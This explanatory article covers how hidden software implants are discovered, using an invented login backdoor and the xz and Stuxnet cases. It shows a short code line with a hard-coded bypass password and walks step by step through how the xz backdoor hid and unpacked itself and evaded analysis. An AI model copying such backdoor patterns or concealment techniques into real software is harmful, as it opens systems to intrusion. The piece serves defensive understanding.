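# How hidden software implants are discovered: runtime anomalies, source review, and what the record implies for AI models

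## What is a hidden implant, and in what ways can one be found?

A hidden implant is code or behavior that someone has concealed in a computer system to serve a person other than the system's owner. An implant that gives access, for instance by letting a stranger log in, is a backdoor. Implants can sit in ordinary programs, in the software inside routers and cameras, and in machine-learning models. Finding them is not yet routine. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) credits luck and manual review with stopping the known attempts to plant backdoors in widely used open-source software, whose source code anyone may read.

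An implant has a trigger, the condition or input that makes it act, and a payload, which is what it does once triggered. Take an invented login program that guards a company's servers. The honest version compares the password that a user types with the company's records and opens a session if the two agree. A dishonest programmer changes one line:

```
if password == "heron-4471" or matches_record(user, password):
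    open_session(user)
```

Anyone who types heron-4471 as the password now gets in under any user name, including the administrator's. The trigger is that string in the password field. The payload skips the check against the records and opens a session. Employees who type their own passwords notice nothing, and neither does a tester who tries a few wrong ones. Random guessing is unlikely to find the string, because there are about 4.8 quadrillion ten-character strings of lowercase letters, digits and hyphens, and a machine that tried a million a second would need roughly 150 years to try them all.

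In *Backdoors*, Thomas and Francillon add two parts to the trigger and the payload. The input source is where the triggering value comes from, such as a network connection or the system clock. The privileged state is the state the attacker ends up in. In the login program, that state is an open session, which honest users also reach routinely, so a session opened with the secret password looks much like any other.

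The definition covers behavior as well as code because a neural network can carry an implant that nobody wrote as a line of code. A network computes its output using a large set of learned numbers called weights, which training adjusts little by little until the outputs on example data come out right. After training, the network combines each input with these fixed weights in layer after layer, producing intermediate values called activations that change with the input. A trojaned model is a network that behaves normally until a trigger appears in its input, then does what an attacker chose. A trojaned spam filter might sort mail correctly except that it lets through every message containing a certain odd phrase. An attacker could cause this by adding spam that contains the phrase, labeled as harmless, to the training data. Someone could find the text heron-4471 in the login program, but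 the filter's weights do not contain its trigger phrase as text.

### From source code to a running program

Programmers write source code, but computers usually run a different file. A project keeps its source in a repository, which records each change as a commit. Reviewers usually read the code there. To publish a version, the maintainers bundle the files into a release archive. A build then turns the source into a binary, a file of machine instructions. During the build, a compiler translates the code, and build scripts pull in dependencies, which are libraries by other people that the program relies on. A distributor then passes the binary to users, who install it.

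The secret password could enter at any of these points.

| Where the attacker acts | What the attacker does | What a reader of the login program's repository finds |
|---|---|---|
| Repository | Gets the extra comparison accepted as a commit | The comparison, on reaching that line |
| Release archive | Adds the comparison to the archive only | Clean source |
| Dependency | Alters a library that the login program calls | Clean source; the change is in another project |
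| Build | Makes the compiler or a build script insert the comparison | Clean source |
| Distribution | Swaps the finished binary for another | Clean source |

It is normal for a release archive to differ from the repository. *Making Releases*, part of the rules of the long-running free-software project GNU, allows an archive to include files that programs generated from the source. *Reproducible Software Releases* describes such archives as the form most users use, often with many generated files included to make building easier. An extra file is therefore no cause for alarm, which helps an attacker who wants to add one. Software hosting sites can also produce an archive automatically from the tagged version in the repository, which would remove the difference. But in a preliminary count in *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (2024), only 10 of about 61 packages relied directly on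 the automatic archive. The count covered packages in Debian, a large Linux distribution, on which popular internet-facing server software depends.

An implant added during the build is even harder to see by reading the source. Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts (SLSA), an industry specification for protecting software on its way to users, treats every link from source to distribution as a place where code can change. An invented case in SLSA's *Threats & mitigations* resembles the login program. An attacker compiles a file with a setting that replaces the call to the authorization check with "true". The build system stores the compiled file and reuses it in later builds. Those builds produce a program that skips the authorization check, although the source file never changed.

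*Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984) describes a compiler implant that persists after its source code is removed. Thompson altered a compiler so that it recognized the source of the Unix login command and produced a version that accepted a known password as well as the real one. Anyone reading the compiler's source would have seen this alteration, so Thompson described a second one, which makes the compiler recognize its own source and insert both alterations whenever it compiles a new compiler. The attacker compiles this version once, installs the binary as the official compiler and restores the original source. From then on, compiling the clean source of either the compiler or the login command still produces an altered program.

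How much anyone can check about a software package after it is built depends on who built it. Solarin, Kalu and colleagues (2026), in *Reproducibility is Not Enough*, contrast Debian, which builds packages on its own machines and records how, with registries such as PyPI (for Python) and npm (for JavaScript), where maintainers build packages wherever they like and upload the result. Those registries have no authoritative record of how a package was built. An attacker can get users to run code that no reviewer has read, either by tampering with the maintainer's build or by skipping it and uploading a malicious file with stolen credentials.

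### Four routes to a discovery

Source review means reading a program's human-written code to look for faults or malice. It works very well against the line containing heron-4471, provided that the line is in the repository and somebody reads it, but neither is certain. Kokkonis and colleagues note that the changes in a single release can run from thousands to millions of lines. A careful attacker also avoids anything as obvious as a plain-text password. SLSA lists the "bugdoor", a malicious change that looks benign to its reviewer, among the threats it does not address.

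Reverse engineering means working out what a compiled program does when its source is missing or not trusted. An analyst uses a disassembler, which turns machine instructions back into a readable listing, and a debugger, which can pause the program and show the contents of its memory. Because the analyst studies the file that users run, this method can find an implant even when the source is clean. It is slow because compiled code has usually lost the names and comments that make source readable, and nobody has time to examine every program on a server this way just in case one contains an implant.

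An integrity check compares two copies or records that should match. The strongest check for the step from source to binary relies on reproducible builds. *Reproducible Builds* (Lamb and Zacchiroli, 2021) defines a build as reproducible if the same source and build dependencies always produce a bit-for-bit identical file. Several independent parties can then build the program and publish its checksum, a short fingerprint that changes when the file does. Users can discard a download with a different checksum without having to understand the code or suspect a problem with it.

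Builds of the same source often differ for harmless reasons. Compilers may write the date or the build folder's name into the file, or process files in whatever order the disk returns them. To find such causes, Debian built each package twice under deliberately different conditions, with the second machine's clock set 18 months ahead. According to Debian's *bits from the release team* (2026), its software now keeps new packages from moving towards the next release if they cannot be reproduced.

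Elsewhere, a mismatch is much weaker evidence of tampering. In *No Snake Oil*, Dietrich and colleagues (2026) used two automatic tools to rebuild popular Python packages, and only 15.4% of one tool's rebuilds and 19.1% of the other's were identical to the published files. Suppose one package in 10,000 carries an implant from a tampered build. With the better tool, about 8,090 of 10,000 rebuilds would fail to match, and only one of those would be the package with the implant. The false positive rate, the share of harmless cases that a detector wrongly flags, would be about 81%.

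When Dietrich and colleagues discounted known harmless differences, the matches rose to 60.2% and 78.9% of the rebuilds that started from the same source. Solarin and colleagues, who also ignored differences such as timestamps and documentation, matched roughly 53 to 87% of completed rebuilds, depending on the registry. But their experiment excluded packages with no usable link to a public repository. Outsiders have no source from which to rebuild such packages, and between 14.7 and 42.4% of packages in the four registries lacked a valid link.

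Integrity checks also miss any implant that is in every copy being compared, and no improvement in tooling can change this. If the attacker got heron-4471 into the repository itself, every faithful rebuild will contain it and all the copies will match. Independent builders who all start from one copy of Thompson's compiler will likewise produce matching copies that contain its backdoor.

The remaining way to find an implant is to notice a runtime anomaly, which is unexpected behavior while a system runs, such as extra processor use, crashes, or unfamiliar traffic. This doesn't require source code or prior suspicion of the program at fault, but the implant must do something visible, and the observer must know how the system normally behaves.

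Software can do some of the work of watching for unusual behavior. Kokkonis and colleagues built a tool, Lily, that feeds machine-generated inputs to a new version of a program for ten minutes, a technique called fuzzing. For each input, Lily records which kinds of request the program makes to the operating system, such as opening a file or starting another program. It raises an alarm only if the pattern is unusual for the new version and the old version does not show it on the same input. In trials, Lily caught on average 90% of backdoored commits and 83% of backdoored releases, with false alarms on 0.2% of safe commits and 4.3% of safe releases. These results are good, but the test set held only 13 backdoored commits and 50 backdoored releases, and researchers had created some of the backdoors for testing. Because Lily looks for what a change has introduced, it also misses implants already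 in the old version. Kokkonis and colleagues recommend first auditing the old version with *ROSA* (2025), another fuzzing tool.

The login program would probably be a hard case for Lily. The fuzzer would have to generate heron-4471, and even then the program would only open a session. If the baseline already includes an ordinary successful login, that session may not look unusual enough to flag.

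### The steps of a discovery

Most discoveries of hidden implants involve at least four steps: noticing a first signal, deciding to investigate, locating the component responsible, and proving malice. Different methods can account for different steps, so there may be more than one answer to how an implant was found.

Suppose an administrator at the company with the doctored login program sees a session under the name of a colleague who is away on a mountain with no phone. This runtime anomaly is the first signal. A stolen password would explain it, so the administrator resets the password and goes back to work. Many signals are pursued no further than this. Two nights later, another session opens under the same account, although nobody has yet told the colleague the new password, and the administrator decides to investigate.

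The fault could lie in the password database, the network or the administrator's own laptop. To narrow it down, the administrator rebuilds the login program from its repository and finds that the installed copy differs. The mismatch alone would mean little, because harmless rebuilds often differ, but it follows two impossible logins and points to a component. An analyst then disassembles the part that differs and finds the comparison with heron-4471. The runtime anomaly prompted the search, the integrity check located the implant, and reverse engineering proved what it was, while source review contributed nothing because the source was clean.

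Proving malice can be the hardest step. Thomas and Francillon require an analyst to recover a backdoor's trigger, its payload and the path between them, and also to show that the developer meant it to be there. A hard-coded password that bypasses the normal check is enough to show intent. A programmer who wanted an excuse might instead leave a buffer overflow, a flaw that lets overlong input overwrite neighboring memory, and keep quiet about how to exploit it. Thomas and Francillon call this a deniable backdoor, and hold that nobody can tell it from an honest mistake on technical evidence alone. The project's history may show who added the flaw and whether the change had any legitimate purpose, but inferring intent from that history requires a judgment about people. Some deliberate implants have presumably been recorded as ordinary bugs.

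Thomas and Francillon write that laborious manual analysis still accounts for the vast majority of detected real-world backdoors. That may well be true of the steps of locating an implant and proving what it is, but it doesn't explain why the analyst examined that program rather than one of the thousands of others on the same machine. What prompts the examination affects dwell time, the time between an implant's arrival and its discovery. Without a prompt, an implant that any competent analyst could work out in an afternoon can remain undiscovered for years.

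The later sections therefore examine which route led to each step of the discovery in each case. The first case is the xz backdoor, where the signal was a little extra processor use.

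## How did extra processor use expose the xz backdoor?

XZ Utils is a free set of programs for compressing files, and most Linux distributions install its library, liblzma, by default. In February 2024 a maintainer using the name Jia Tan released version 5.6.0 with a backdoor in that library. The backdoor targeted sshd, the OpenSSH server program that administrators use to log in to machines over a network. It let only the holder of a particular private key run any command on an affected machine without logging in.

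OpenSSH itself does not use liblzma. *Wolves in the Repository* (2025) explains that some Linux distributions alter sshd to work with systemd, the program that starts and stops services, and that systemd's library loads liblzma. XZ Utils was also an easy target, with one developer and about ten active people in its chat channel. According to *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024), Jia Tan sent a first, harmless patch in October 2021. During 2022, several accounts, probably fake, pressed the maintainer, Lasse Collin, to hand over control, and by the end of that year Jia Tan could commit changes directly. Version 5.6.0 came out on February 24, 2024 and reached Debian's unstable branch two days later. Andres Freund reported the backdoor privately on March 28, for a dwell time of 33 days from release.

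### A noisy benchmark

Freund is a Microsoft engineer who works on the database PostgreSQL. In March 2024 he was measuring whether a colleague's change slowed down queries on data already in memory. The slowdown was only 1 to 2%, he told the podcast Oxide and Friends (2024), and repeated runs varied more than he liked, so he checked whether anything else was using the machine. A list of running processes showed sshd occasionally using a fair amount of processor time.

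Some sshd activity was normal because the machine was open to the internet, where automated programs constantly try to log in to any server they can reach. But these attempts used wrong user names, and Freund had switched off password logins, so sshd should have rejected them almost at once. He saw the sshd processes more than once during several hours of benchmarking before he decided that he needed an explanation.

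Freund ran a profiler, which samples a program as it runs to measure where it spends its time. Much of the time was spent in liblzma, at addresses that the profiler could not match to any symbol, the name a compiled file keeps for a function. A refused login has nothing to compress, so liblzma should not have been running. Freund first wondered whether the profiler was at fault. He then tried a debugger, but it repeatedly failed to trace which function had called which.

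After perhaps an hour, Freund realized that this looked familiar. About a month earlier, following some package updates, his automated PostgreSQL tests had produced an odd warning from Valgrind, a tool that checks a program's memory accesses while it runs. He had failed to explain the warning, left on a trip and silenced it. His command history still showed what he had examined, and he traced the warning to the same library. He told the Oxide and Friends podcast that without the earlier warning he might not have pursued the processor use.

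Freund noticed a process using a lot of processor time for no reason on a machine that he was trying to keep quiet. News reports soon simplified this. Hackaday's *Security Alert* attributed the discovery to logins that took longer than expected, and TechSpot's *Linux could have been brought down by backdoor* reported that Freund noticed a 600-millisecond delay. Freund corrected this version on the day of the disclosure in *A backdoor in xz*, a discussion on the Linux news site LWN, where he wrote as andresfreund (2024) that he had not noticed the delay while logging in. That is easy to believe, since a slow network can add half a second to a login.

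Freund at first thought that someone had compromised Debian's package, and he began a report to Debian. Then he found the same code in the archives published by the xz project itself. Normally he would have written to the project's security contact, but that was Jia Tan, so he alerted Debian and a private list of distributors instead. He went public on March 29, a few days after he first became suspicious.

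### The cost of setting up

Freund measured the delay only after he had started investigating. His public warning, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024), reports timings for a login to a nonexistent account. The refusal took 0.299 seconds with a clean liblzma and 0.807 seconds with the backdoored one. The login program on the user's side used 0.202 seconds of processor time in both runs, so the extra half second came from the server. The delay also appeared when he ran sshd with the option -h, which does not start a server. On an older machine, that command took about 0.5 seconds when the backdoor was active and about 0.01 seconds when it was not.

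The delay came from the way programs start on Linux. Before a program's own code runs, the dynamic linker loads the libraries it needs and fills in a table with the addresses of the functions it will call. For safety, many distributions build sshd so that the linker fills in the whole table at the start and then makes it read-only. Before the linker locked the table, the backdoor had to change one entry, the address of RSA_public_decrypt, which sshd calls when it checks certain login keys.

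The backdoor got in through ifunc, a feature that lets a library run a small function during loading, usually to pick the fastest version of a routine for the processor. liblzma adopted ifunc in June 2023 for what *Wolves in the Repository* calls a small performance boost. The backdoor replaced two of these small functions, so its code ran while the table was still writable.

At that stage the linker had not finished connecting the libraries, so the backdoor could not simply call the functions it needed. It had to look them up in the symbol tables, the lists of function names and addresses that the linker uses. The attackers encoded the names it searched for, because an analyst who saw a name such as RSA_public_decrypt as plain text in a compression library would wonder why it was there. Checking a symbol against the encoded names took several processor cycles for each character, and the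 backdoor did this for symbol after symbol in the libraries that sshd had loaded.

Freund told Oxide and Friends that this matching took up nearly all of the roughly 500 milliseconds. The obfuscation, which was meant to hinder reverse engineering, had caused the runtime anomaly, and he said he would probably not have noticed anything if there had been less of it.

The backdoor took up extra processor time even when no attacker was using it. sshd starts a fresh copy of itself for each connection, so every failed password guess by a bot set off the whole search again. At least one reader of the security mailing list could not see how a refused login would reach the replaced function. Freund (2024), in *xz backdoor prevention using hosts.deny?*, answered that the slow part was the backdoor's initialization, which finished before sshd's own code began. An implant that has to initialize every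 time a program starts can therefore be noticed long before an attacker uses it. The invented heron-4471 line needs no initialization, and its single comparison would never show up in a list of busy processes.

The xz attackers could have avoided most of the extra processor use. Freund thought they could have done only the minimum work at load time, adding perhaps tens of milliseconds, and postponed the rest until someone connected. It looked to him as if less experienced people had overused techniques that others had built for them. The attackers may also have been in a hurry. On February 29 a developer proposed that systemd's library stop loading liblzma at startup, a change that would probably have defeated the attack. Mentions of the plan went back to late January, and *Timeline of the xz open source attack* relays a suggestion that the plan made the attackers bring their release forward.

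### Checks meant to keep analysts away

The backdoor did its processor-intensive work only under certain conditions. Freund found some of these conditions by experiment and warned that there were others he had not fully traced.

| Condition for the backdoor to activate | What it made harder |
|---|---|
| The program's name is /usr/sbin/sshd | Reproducing the slowdown in another program that loads liblzma |
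| The variable TERM, which describes a user's terminal, is not set | Starting sshd by hand from a terminal |
| The variables LD_DEBUG and LD_PROFILE are not set | Using the linker's own diagnostic output |
| The variable LANG, which sets the language, is set | Testing in a completely empty environment |
| No debugger is detected | Using the debugger rr, and in some situations gdb |

These checks slowed Freund down. When he started sshd from a terminal, the problem disappeared, and it came back only when systemd started the program. But the difference was suspicious, because an ordinary performance bug should not depend on how the server was started.

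Once Freund had worked out the conditions, he could switch the backdoor on by clearing every environment variable except LANG, and off by adding TERM. He recorded both kinds of run with Intel Processor Trace, a processor feature that logs a program's exact path without slowing it much, and looked for the point where the two paths separated. This let him avoid the unreliable debugger. It also suited his skills. He wrote in the warning that he was neither a security researcher nor a reverse engineer, but comparing a fast run with a slow one is routine performance work.

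A second group of checks ran earlier, when someone compiled the library. The hidden build script stopped unless it was running on 64-bit x86 Linux, with the GCC compiler and the GNU linker, as part of building a Debian or RPM package. Freund thought the packaging requirement was probably meant to frustrate investigators, since a developer who compiled the suspect release by hand would get a clean library.

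### What a reader of the source could have seen

The attackers split the implant between two places. Most of it was in the public repository, inside two files that looked like test data. Developers test compression libraries on damaged and unusual files, and the xz project already had a folder of them. *The xz attack shell script* (2024) points out that the folder's description, written long before Jia Tan arrived, said that many of the files had been made by hand in a hex editor and that there was no better source than the files themselves. A reviewer who opened one of the new files would have seen the seemingly meaningless bytes they expected.

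The instructions for unpacking them were missing from the repository. They were in build-to-host.m4, a supporting file for the build that appeared only in the release archives. Freund's warning singled out one line of it, and a comparison with the standard version shows several other altered lines around it. The attackers had even raised the file's version number and updated its copyright year. The unpacking went as follows:

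1. While preparing the build, the altered file searched the release for a particular pattern of hash marks and found it in a test file named as a corrupt archive.
2. It swapped a few characters in that file back to their proper values, which repaired the archive, then decompressed it and ran the short script inside.
3. The short script decompressed the second test file, alternately threw away 1,024 bytes and kept 2,048, undid a simple substitution cipher and decompressed the result. This gave a longer script.
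4. The longer script ran the build checks and edited the build instructions. Later in the build, a compiled piece of code, also hidden in the second test file, went into liblzma.

Someone reading only the repository could not have seen this happen. Reading the archive gave a better chance of spotting the file responsible, but developers seldom read that kind of file, and a comparison with the repository would have listed it among other, harmless files found only in the archive.

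The split also misled Freund. While trying to reproduce the problem, he happened to download the archive that GitHub generates automatically from the repository. His build was clean, and for a while he assumed he had built it wrong.

The repository did contain one clue. Version 5.6.0 included the new test files but no test that used them. Freund found this suspicious once he was looking, but he told Oxide and Friends that the attackers could have put the build instructions in the repository too and nobody would have noticed.

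### The errors that Jia Tan explained away

Others besides Freund saw the Valgrind errors. On March 4, Scott (2024) told the Linux distribution Fedora in *Invalid writes regression in liblzma.so* that about 130 of roughly 1,000 tests in a software project called PCP had started failing over a weekend. Richard Jones, who handled the report, reproduced the fault with a program that only loaded liblzma. Valgrind counted 112 errors, and its trace showed the function through which the backdoor started.

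Jones's program was not called sshd, so the backdoor should have stayed inactive. But the code that checked whether to activate had to run first, and it evidently ran in any program that loaded the library. When frame pointers, which help profilers follow function calls, were present, the backdoor used the wrong position in the stack, the area of memory where a program keeps track of those calls. Freund believed the attackers had assumed a stack layout without frame pointers. Fedora had just begun to include them by default, and Freund included them in his own test builds to make profiling easier.

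On the day of the report, Jones rebuilt the library with ifunc turned off, and the errors stopped. This almost certainly also removed the backdoor, which Fedora's packagers did not yet know about, because the hidden build script quits if ifunc is unavailable.

On March 8, Jia Tan made a change presented as a fix for the Valgrind problem, which *Timeline of the xz open source attack* calls a misdirection. The real fix came on March 9, when Jia Tan replaced the two test files, saying that the originals had used random data from one machine and that a fixed starting value would make the files easier to recreate. Version 5.6.1 was released the same day. Its release notes, quoted in an Ubuntu request titled *Sync xz-utils 5.6.1-1 (main) from Debian unstable (main)*, said that liblzma had caused Valgrind to "falsely" report an invalid write. Fedora adopted the new version and closed Scott's report.

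The story was believable partly because 5.6.0 also had a real fault in its use of ifunc. Gentoo users had reported a crash on the day of the release. In their discussion (Gentoo, 2024), the developer Sam James suspected the compiler and contacted Jia Tan. James told GCC's developers that Jia Tan had helped reduce the problem to a small example. By early March, people had therefore seen Jia Tan deal competently with a real compiler problem in the same part of the library. Even after the disclosure, Mark Wielaard commented on Scott's report that the false fix sounded somewhat plausible and that he doubted he would have recognized it as suspicious.

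The attackers next used the errors to promote the new version. On March 25 an account named Hans Jansen asked Debian to adopt 5.6.1. A supporting message in Debian's *RFS* (2024) argued that the update removed a false warning that could interfere with other projects' tests. Debian adopted 5.6.1 on March 27, one day before Freund's private report. Freund said he was not sure he would have worked out the problem if Debian had adopted 5.6.1 sooner.

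Several capable people therefore had the first signal for weeks, but they investigated it in good faith as a bug and stopped when the bug went away. Freund later concluded that the Valgrind reports alone contained enough information to find the problem. He got further because a second anomaly, which had no ready explanation, pointed to the same library.

### Luck, skill and open source

Freund described the find on Mastodon as accidental and said it had "required a lot of coincidences." He listed several on the podcast Oxide and Friends. In other release cycles, he had spent more time reviewing code than measuring speed. His test server had slower cores than his laptop and its turbo mode was off, which exaggerated the delay. If he had left password logins enabled, he could reasonably have blamed the processor use on the cryptography used to check passwords.

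Others saw a success for open source. Bryan Cantrill, one of the podcast's hosts, argued that openness had forced the attackers to go to great lengths to hide their code, and that this might have caused the extra processor use that exposed the backdoor. Freund disagreed with the second part, saying that the trick with the archives affected only how the code got into the build, not how fast it ran.

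Open source helped mainly after the first signal. Freund could read the build scripts, compare the archive with the repository and look up who had added the test files. Florian Weimer extracted the injected code, and within about a week other volunteers had worked out how the attacker's key gave access. Collin later reviewed the project's commits. In his notes on Tukaani, the project's website, he cleared one change that outsiders had found suspicious because of its time zone. All this would have been much harder with a closed product. But the repository and archives had already been public for a month when Freund began investigating, and no one reading them had reported a problem.

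The first signal can fairly be called luck, but most people would not have followed it up. Freund told the podcast that he dislikes not understanding why something is using the processor, and he had spent years learning how to find out. He was unsure how long the backdoor would have lasted without him. He did not think it would have lasted years, because someone would eventually have looked into the slow logins. But if a later version had cut the delay to a few milliseconds, he thought it would most likely have been found by someone investigating an actual break-in. The affected versions had mostly reached test releases, and LWN's *Free software's not-so-eXZellent adventure* judged that the backdoor had apparently been discovered before anyone exploited it.

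More recent experiments suggest ways to depend less on someone like Freund. *Binary Diff Summarization using Large Language Models* (2025) had language models summarize the differences between compiled copies of liblzma from versions 5.4.7 and 5.6.0, then judge whether the changes were malicious. OpenAI's GPT-5 flagged the backdoored version, describing some functions as atypical for the library. The smaller GPT-5 mini classified it as harmless when working from its own summaries, but correctly classified it as malicious when given GPT-5's. Because the comparison used the compiled library, hiding code in test files and archives would not have defeated it. The result is promising, but GPT-5's training data may well have included descriptions of the xz attack, and a single known case cannot show how often the method would flag harmless updates.

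*MergeShuffle* (2026) tried removing the backdoor without detecting it first. The tool rebuilds a library from the code that a program uses in normal operation. The experimenters ran a server with the compromised liblzma, logged in the ordinary way and rebuilt the library from that activity. Ordinary logins still worked afterwards, but the backdoor login failed, presumably because nobody had used the attacker's route during the recording, so the code for it was left out. The method doesn't require anyone to suspect a backdoor or notice an anomaly, but it could also remove a legitimate feature that nobody used during the recording.

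## How did unexplained reboots lead to Stuxnet?

Stuxnet was a worm, a program that copies itself from one computer to the next. Its makers designed the payload to damage the uranium centrifuges at Natanz in Iran without the plant's operators noticing. But the worm had to spread through ordinary Windows computers to get there, and in June 2010 some of those computers kept crashing.

### Crashes on freshly installed machines

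Sergey Ulasen led antivirus development at VirusBlokAda, a small security company in Minsk, Belarus. He later told the story in a Kaspersky interview, *The Man Who Found Stuxnet*. VirusBlokAda's support staff had passed him a report from a customer in Iran of random reboots and blue screens, the errors Windows displays when it crashes. Ulasen suspected a misconfiguration or a conflict between installed programs, both common causes, and asked what software the customer was running.

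Ulasen changed his mind when he heard that many other computers on the same network had the fault, including some on which administrators had just reinstalled Windows. Reinstalling Windows on a wiped disk removes bad settings and clashing programs, so neither could have caused the crashes on those machines. The cause had to be something that a reinstallation leaves in place, such as the hardware, or something that came back afterwards. Hardware rarely fails in the same way on many computers at once. According to the journalist Kim Zetter, in *Countdown to Zero Day*, Ulasen now suspected that a worm was reinfecting each machine after it was cleaned, and that a rootkit, a program that hides other files and programs, was concealing the worm.

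Ulasen and his contact in Iran, who was also a friend, first tried to solve the problem by phone while Ulasen was at a wedding. The following Monday he connected to one of the infected computers. He and his colleague Oleg Kupreev picked out six suspicious files and spent several days working out what they did. One was indeed a rootkit, which ran in the kernel, the core of Windows, and hid four shortcut files on USB sticks. Windows reads a shortcut file to draw its icon, and reading these files was enough to start the worm. When Ulasen plugged an infected stick into a fully updated Windows 7 computer, the worm installed itself, so Microsoft evidently had no fix for the flaw.

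The hard part was getting someone to investigate. After that, little more was needed to show that the software was malicious, because no legitimate driver hides files on a USB stick and breaks into Windows through an unknown flaw.

An engineer in Iran had come close to discovering Stuxnet almost a year earlier. Zetter's *An Unprecedented Look at Stuxnet, the World's First Digital Weapon* describes a July 2009 post on a Siemens user forum by an engineer at Neda, a control-systems company that Stuxnet had infected two weeks before. All the company's PCs were showing the same error in a file belonging to Step 7, the Siemens software for programming industrial controllers. The engineer had noticed that a clean computer developed the error when files were moved to it by flash drive but not by CD, which correctly pointed to flash drives as the carrier. But virus scans found nothing, and there is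 no sign in the discussion that anyone solved the problem. The known infections with this version of Stuxnet began on June 23, 2009, so the dwell time was just under a year.

### Valid signatures and clean scans

VirusBlokAda's support team had scanned the Iranian computer remotely and found nothing before calling in Ulasen. Antivirus scanners rely heavily on patterns taken from malware that someone has already analyzed, and nobody had analyzed this worm. A kernel rootkit can also interfere with detection because it runs with the same privileges as the scanner.

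The worm's two drivers, small programs that it installed in the kernel, also carried valid digital signatures from Realtek, a Taiwanese hardware maker. A software company signs a file with a secret key, and Windows checks the signature using a certificate that ties the key to the company. This integrity check shows that the file has not changed since someone with the key signed it, but not whether the code is harmless or whether the signer stole the key. Windows 7 would normally have warned the user about an unsigned driver, but it installed these two silently because they were signed.

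The signatures may also have protected the worm from experts. Kupreev and Ulasen (2010) wrote in *Trojan-Spy.0485 And Malware-Cryptor.Win32.Inject.gen.2 Review* that signed drivers misled anti-rootkit tools. They also thought that antivirus companies had probably screened out samples of the drivers when first sorting incoming files. If so, the signatures kept analysts from opening the files. Few people in the industry expected malware signed with a stolen certificate. Zetter notes that on the day Ulasen went public, a researcher at the security company F-Secure published a presentation saying that nobody had yet found any.

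Ulasen first wrote privately to Microsoft and Realtek but received no answer. On July 12 he described the worm on a public security forum, in a post titled *Rootkit.TmpHider* (Ulasen, 2010). The certificate authority Verisign revoked Realtek's certificate on July 16. On July 17 the security company ESET found another Stuxnet driver, signed with the certificate of a second Taiwanese company, JMicron.

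### What made the computers crash?

Nobody has established what caused the reboots. Zetter reports that they did not occur on the other machines later found to be infected, which numbered about 100,000 by the end of September 2010. Some researchers therefore suspect that one of the worm's drivers clashed with VirusBlokAda's antivirus software. The attackers had apparently tested Stuxnet against the large antivirus companies' scanners but not against this one. Researchers at Kaspersky Lab thought the crash happened when the driver injected the worm's main file into memory, but when they tried to reproduce it, the test machine crashed only some of the time.

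The driver could plausibly have caused the reboots. Chappell shows in *The MRXCLS.SYS Malware Loader* that it started every time Windows did and injected the worm into services.exe, a program that runs on every Windows computer. An error in a kernel driver can crash the whole system, and one that recurred at every start would cause a reboot loop. But Chappell does not identify any such error.

If the suspicion is right, Ulasen's first guess of a conflict between two programs was partly correct, but one of the programs was a worm. The control experiment of reinstalling the system would not have ruled out the antivirus scanner as part of the cause, because administrators usually put antivirus software back when they rebuild a computer.

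Ulasen found Stuxnet without ever learning exactly what had caused the reboots. The cause was clearer in other cases. In February 2010, some Windows computers began restarting repeatedly after a security update. Microsoft's *Restart Issues After Installing MS10-015 and the Alureon Rootkit* (2010) attributes the restarts to a rootkit called Alureon, based on memory dumps (saved copies of memory) from several customers' machines. Freund likewise traced the xz delay to a particular piece of code.

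### Normal readings at Natanz

The sabotage took place on industrial controllers, small computers that run equipment and have no screen or keyboard. Engineers program them from a Windows computer running Step 7, and operators may monitor the equipment with separate display software such as Siemens's WinCC. According to *To Kill a Centrifuge* (Langner, 2013), the version of Stuxnet found in 2010 raised the speed of the centrifuge rotors from 63,000 revolutions per minute to 84,600 for 15 minutes. About a month later, it took 50 minutes to slow them to 120 and bring them back up. A rotor vibrates as it passes through certain critical speeds, and it can break each time.

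A suspicious engineer who read the controller's program would probably have found nothing wrong. *W32 Stuxnet Dossier* (Falliere, O Murchu and Chien, 2011), the main analysis by the security company Symantec, explains why. Step 7 communicates with controllers through a library of 109 functions. Stuxnet replaced this library with its own version, which passed 93 of the functions straight to the original and intercepted the other 16, including those that read and list the controller's code. When someone asked to see an infected block of code, the false library removed the malicious part before displaying it. It also left Stuxnet's own blocks out of the list. Comparing the controller's program with a stored copy would have failed for the same reason if done through an infected computer, although the changes were easy to see from a clean one.

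The displays would have looked normal too, though analysts disagree about how Stuxnet achieved this. Falliere and colleagues write that it recorded the motors' earlier operating frequencies and played them back to WinCC during the attack. Ralph Langner, a German specialist in the security of industrial control systems, says it is a common misconception that this attack used playback. By his analysis, the recording was part of an earlier attack, which closed valves to raise the gas pressure in the centrifuges. In that attack, Stuxnet recorded 21 seconds of sensor readings and fed them in a loop to the controller's legitimate program, which kept running but no longer controlled anything. OTbase's *The Stuxnet Story*, Langner's later retelling, adds that the false readings were meant mainly to deceive the program and only secondarily to deceive people.

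The speed attack was cruder. It suspended the legitimate program, so the speed values in the controller's memory stopped updating. The frozen values looked right because rotor speed hardly changes in normal operation. Langner bases his argument on the controller's code, while Symantec's analysts place the playback in the Windows library. In both accounts, someone watching the speeds through an infected system would have seen nothing unusual, although Langner was not sure that Natanz used WinCC to monitor them.

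Stuxnet also caused anomalies elsewhere. The sound of the centrifuges would have changed audibly as they sped up, and at 120 revolutions per minute they would have gone almost silent. Langner wrote in 2013 that staff in the hall could have noticed if they had taken off their protective headsets. In the later retelling, the operators must have heard the change, but this is an inference from the physics. An infected WinCC computer also queried the controllers every five seconds for data that only Stuxnet used. This traffic was impossible to miss in Langner's laboratory, but it seems nobody at the plant was recording it.

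The Windows part was far more conspicuous. An earlier version, which researchers recognized only years after its release, could spread by itself only through infected Step 7 project files. Langner suspects that the attackers later lost their means of carrying the worm to the right computers by hand and so equipped it to spread through networks and on USB sticks. To do this, they added stolen certificates and several zero-days, which are flaws still unknown to the software's maker. These additions got the worm onto far more machines, including those of a VirusBlokAda customer, and made it look important to any analyst who examined it.

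### The centrifuges that inspectors counted

Nuclear inspectors from the International Atomic Energy Agency (IAEA) had noticed that something was wrong at Natanz before Ulasen heard about the reboots. In January 2010, they realized that the plant was replacing centrifuges unusually fast. Zetter (2011) reported that Iran normally replaced up to 10% a year, or about 800 of the roughly 8,700 then installed. Surveillance footage showed workers removing far more than that, and later estimates put the total at between 1,000 and 2,000 in a few months.

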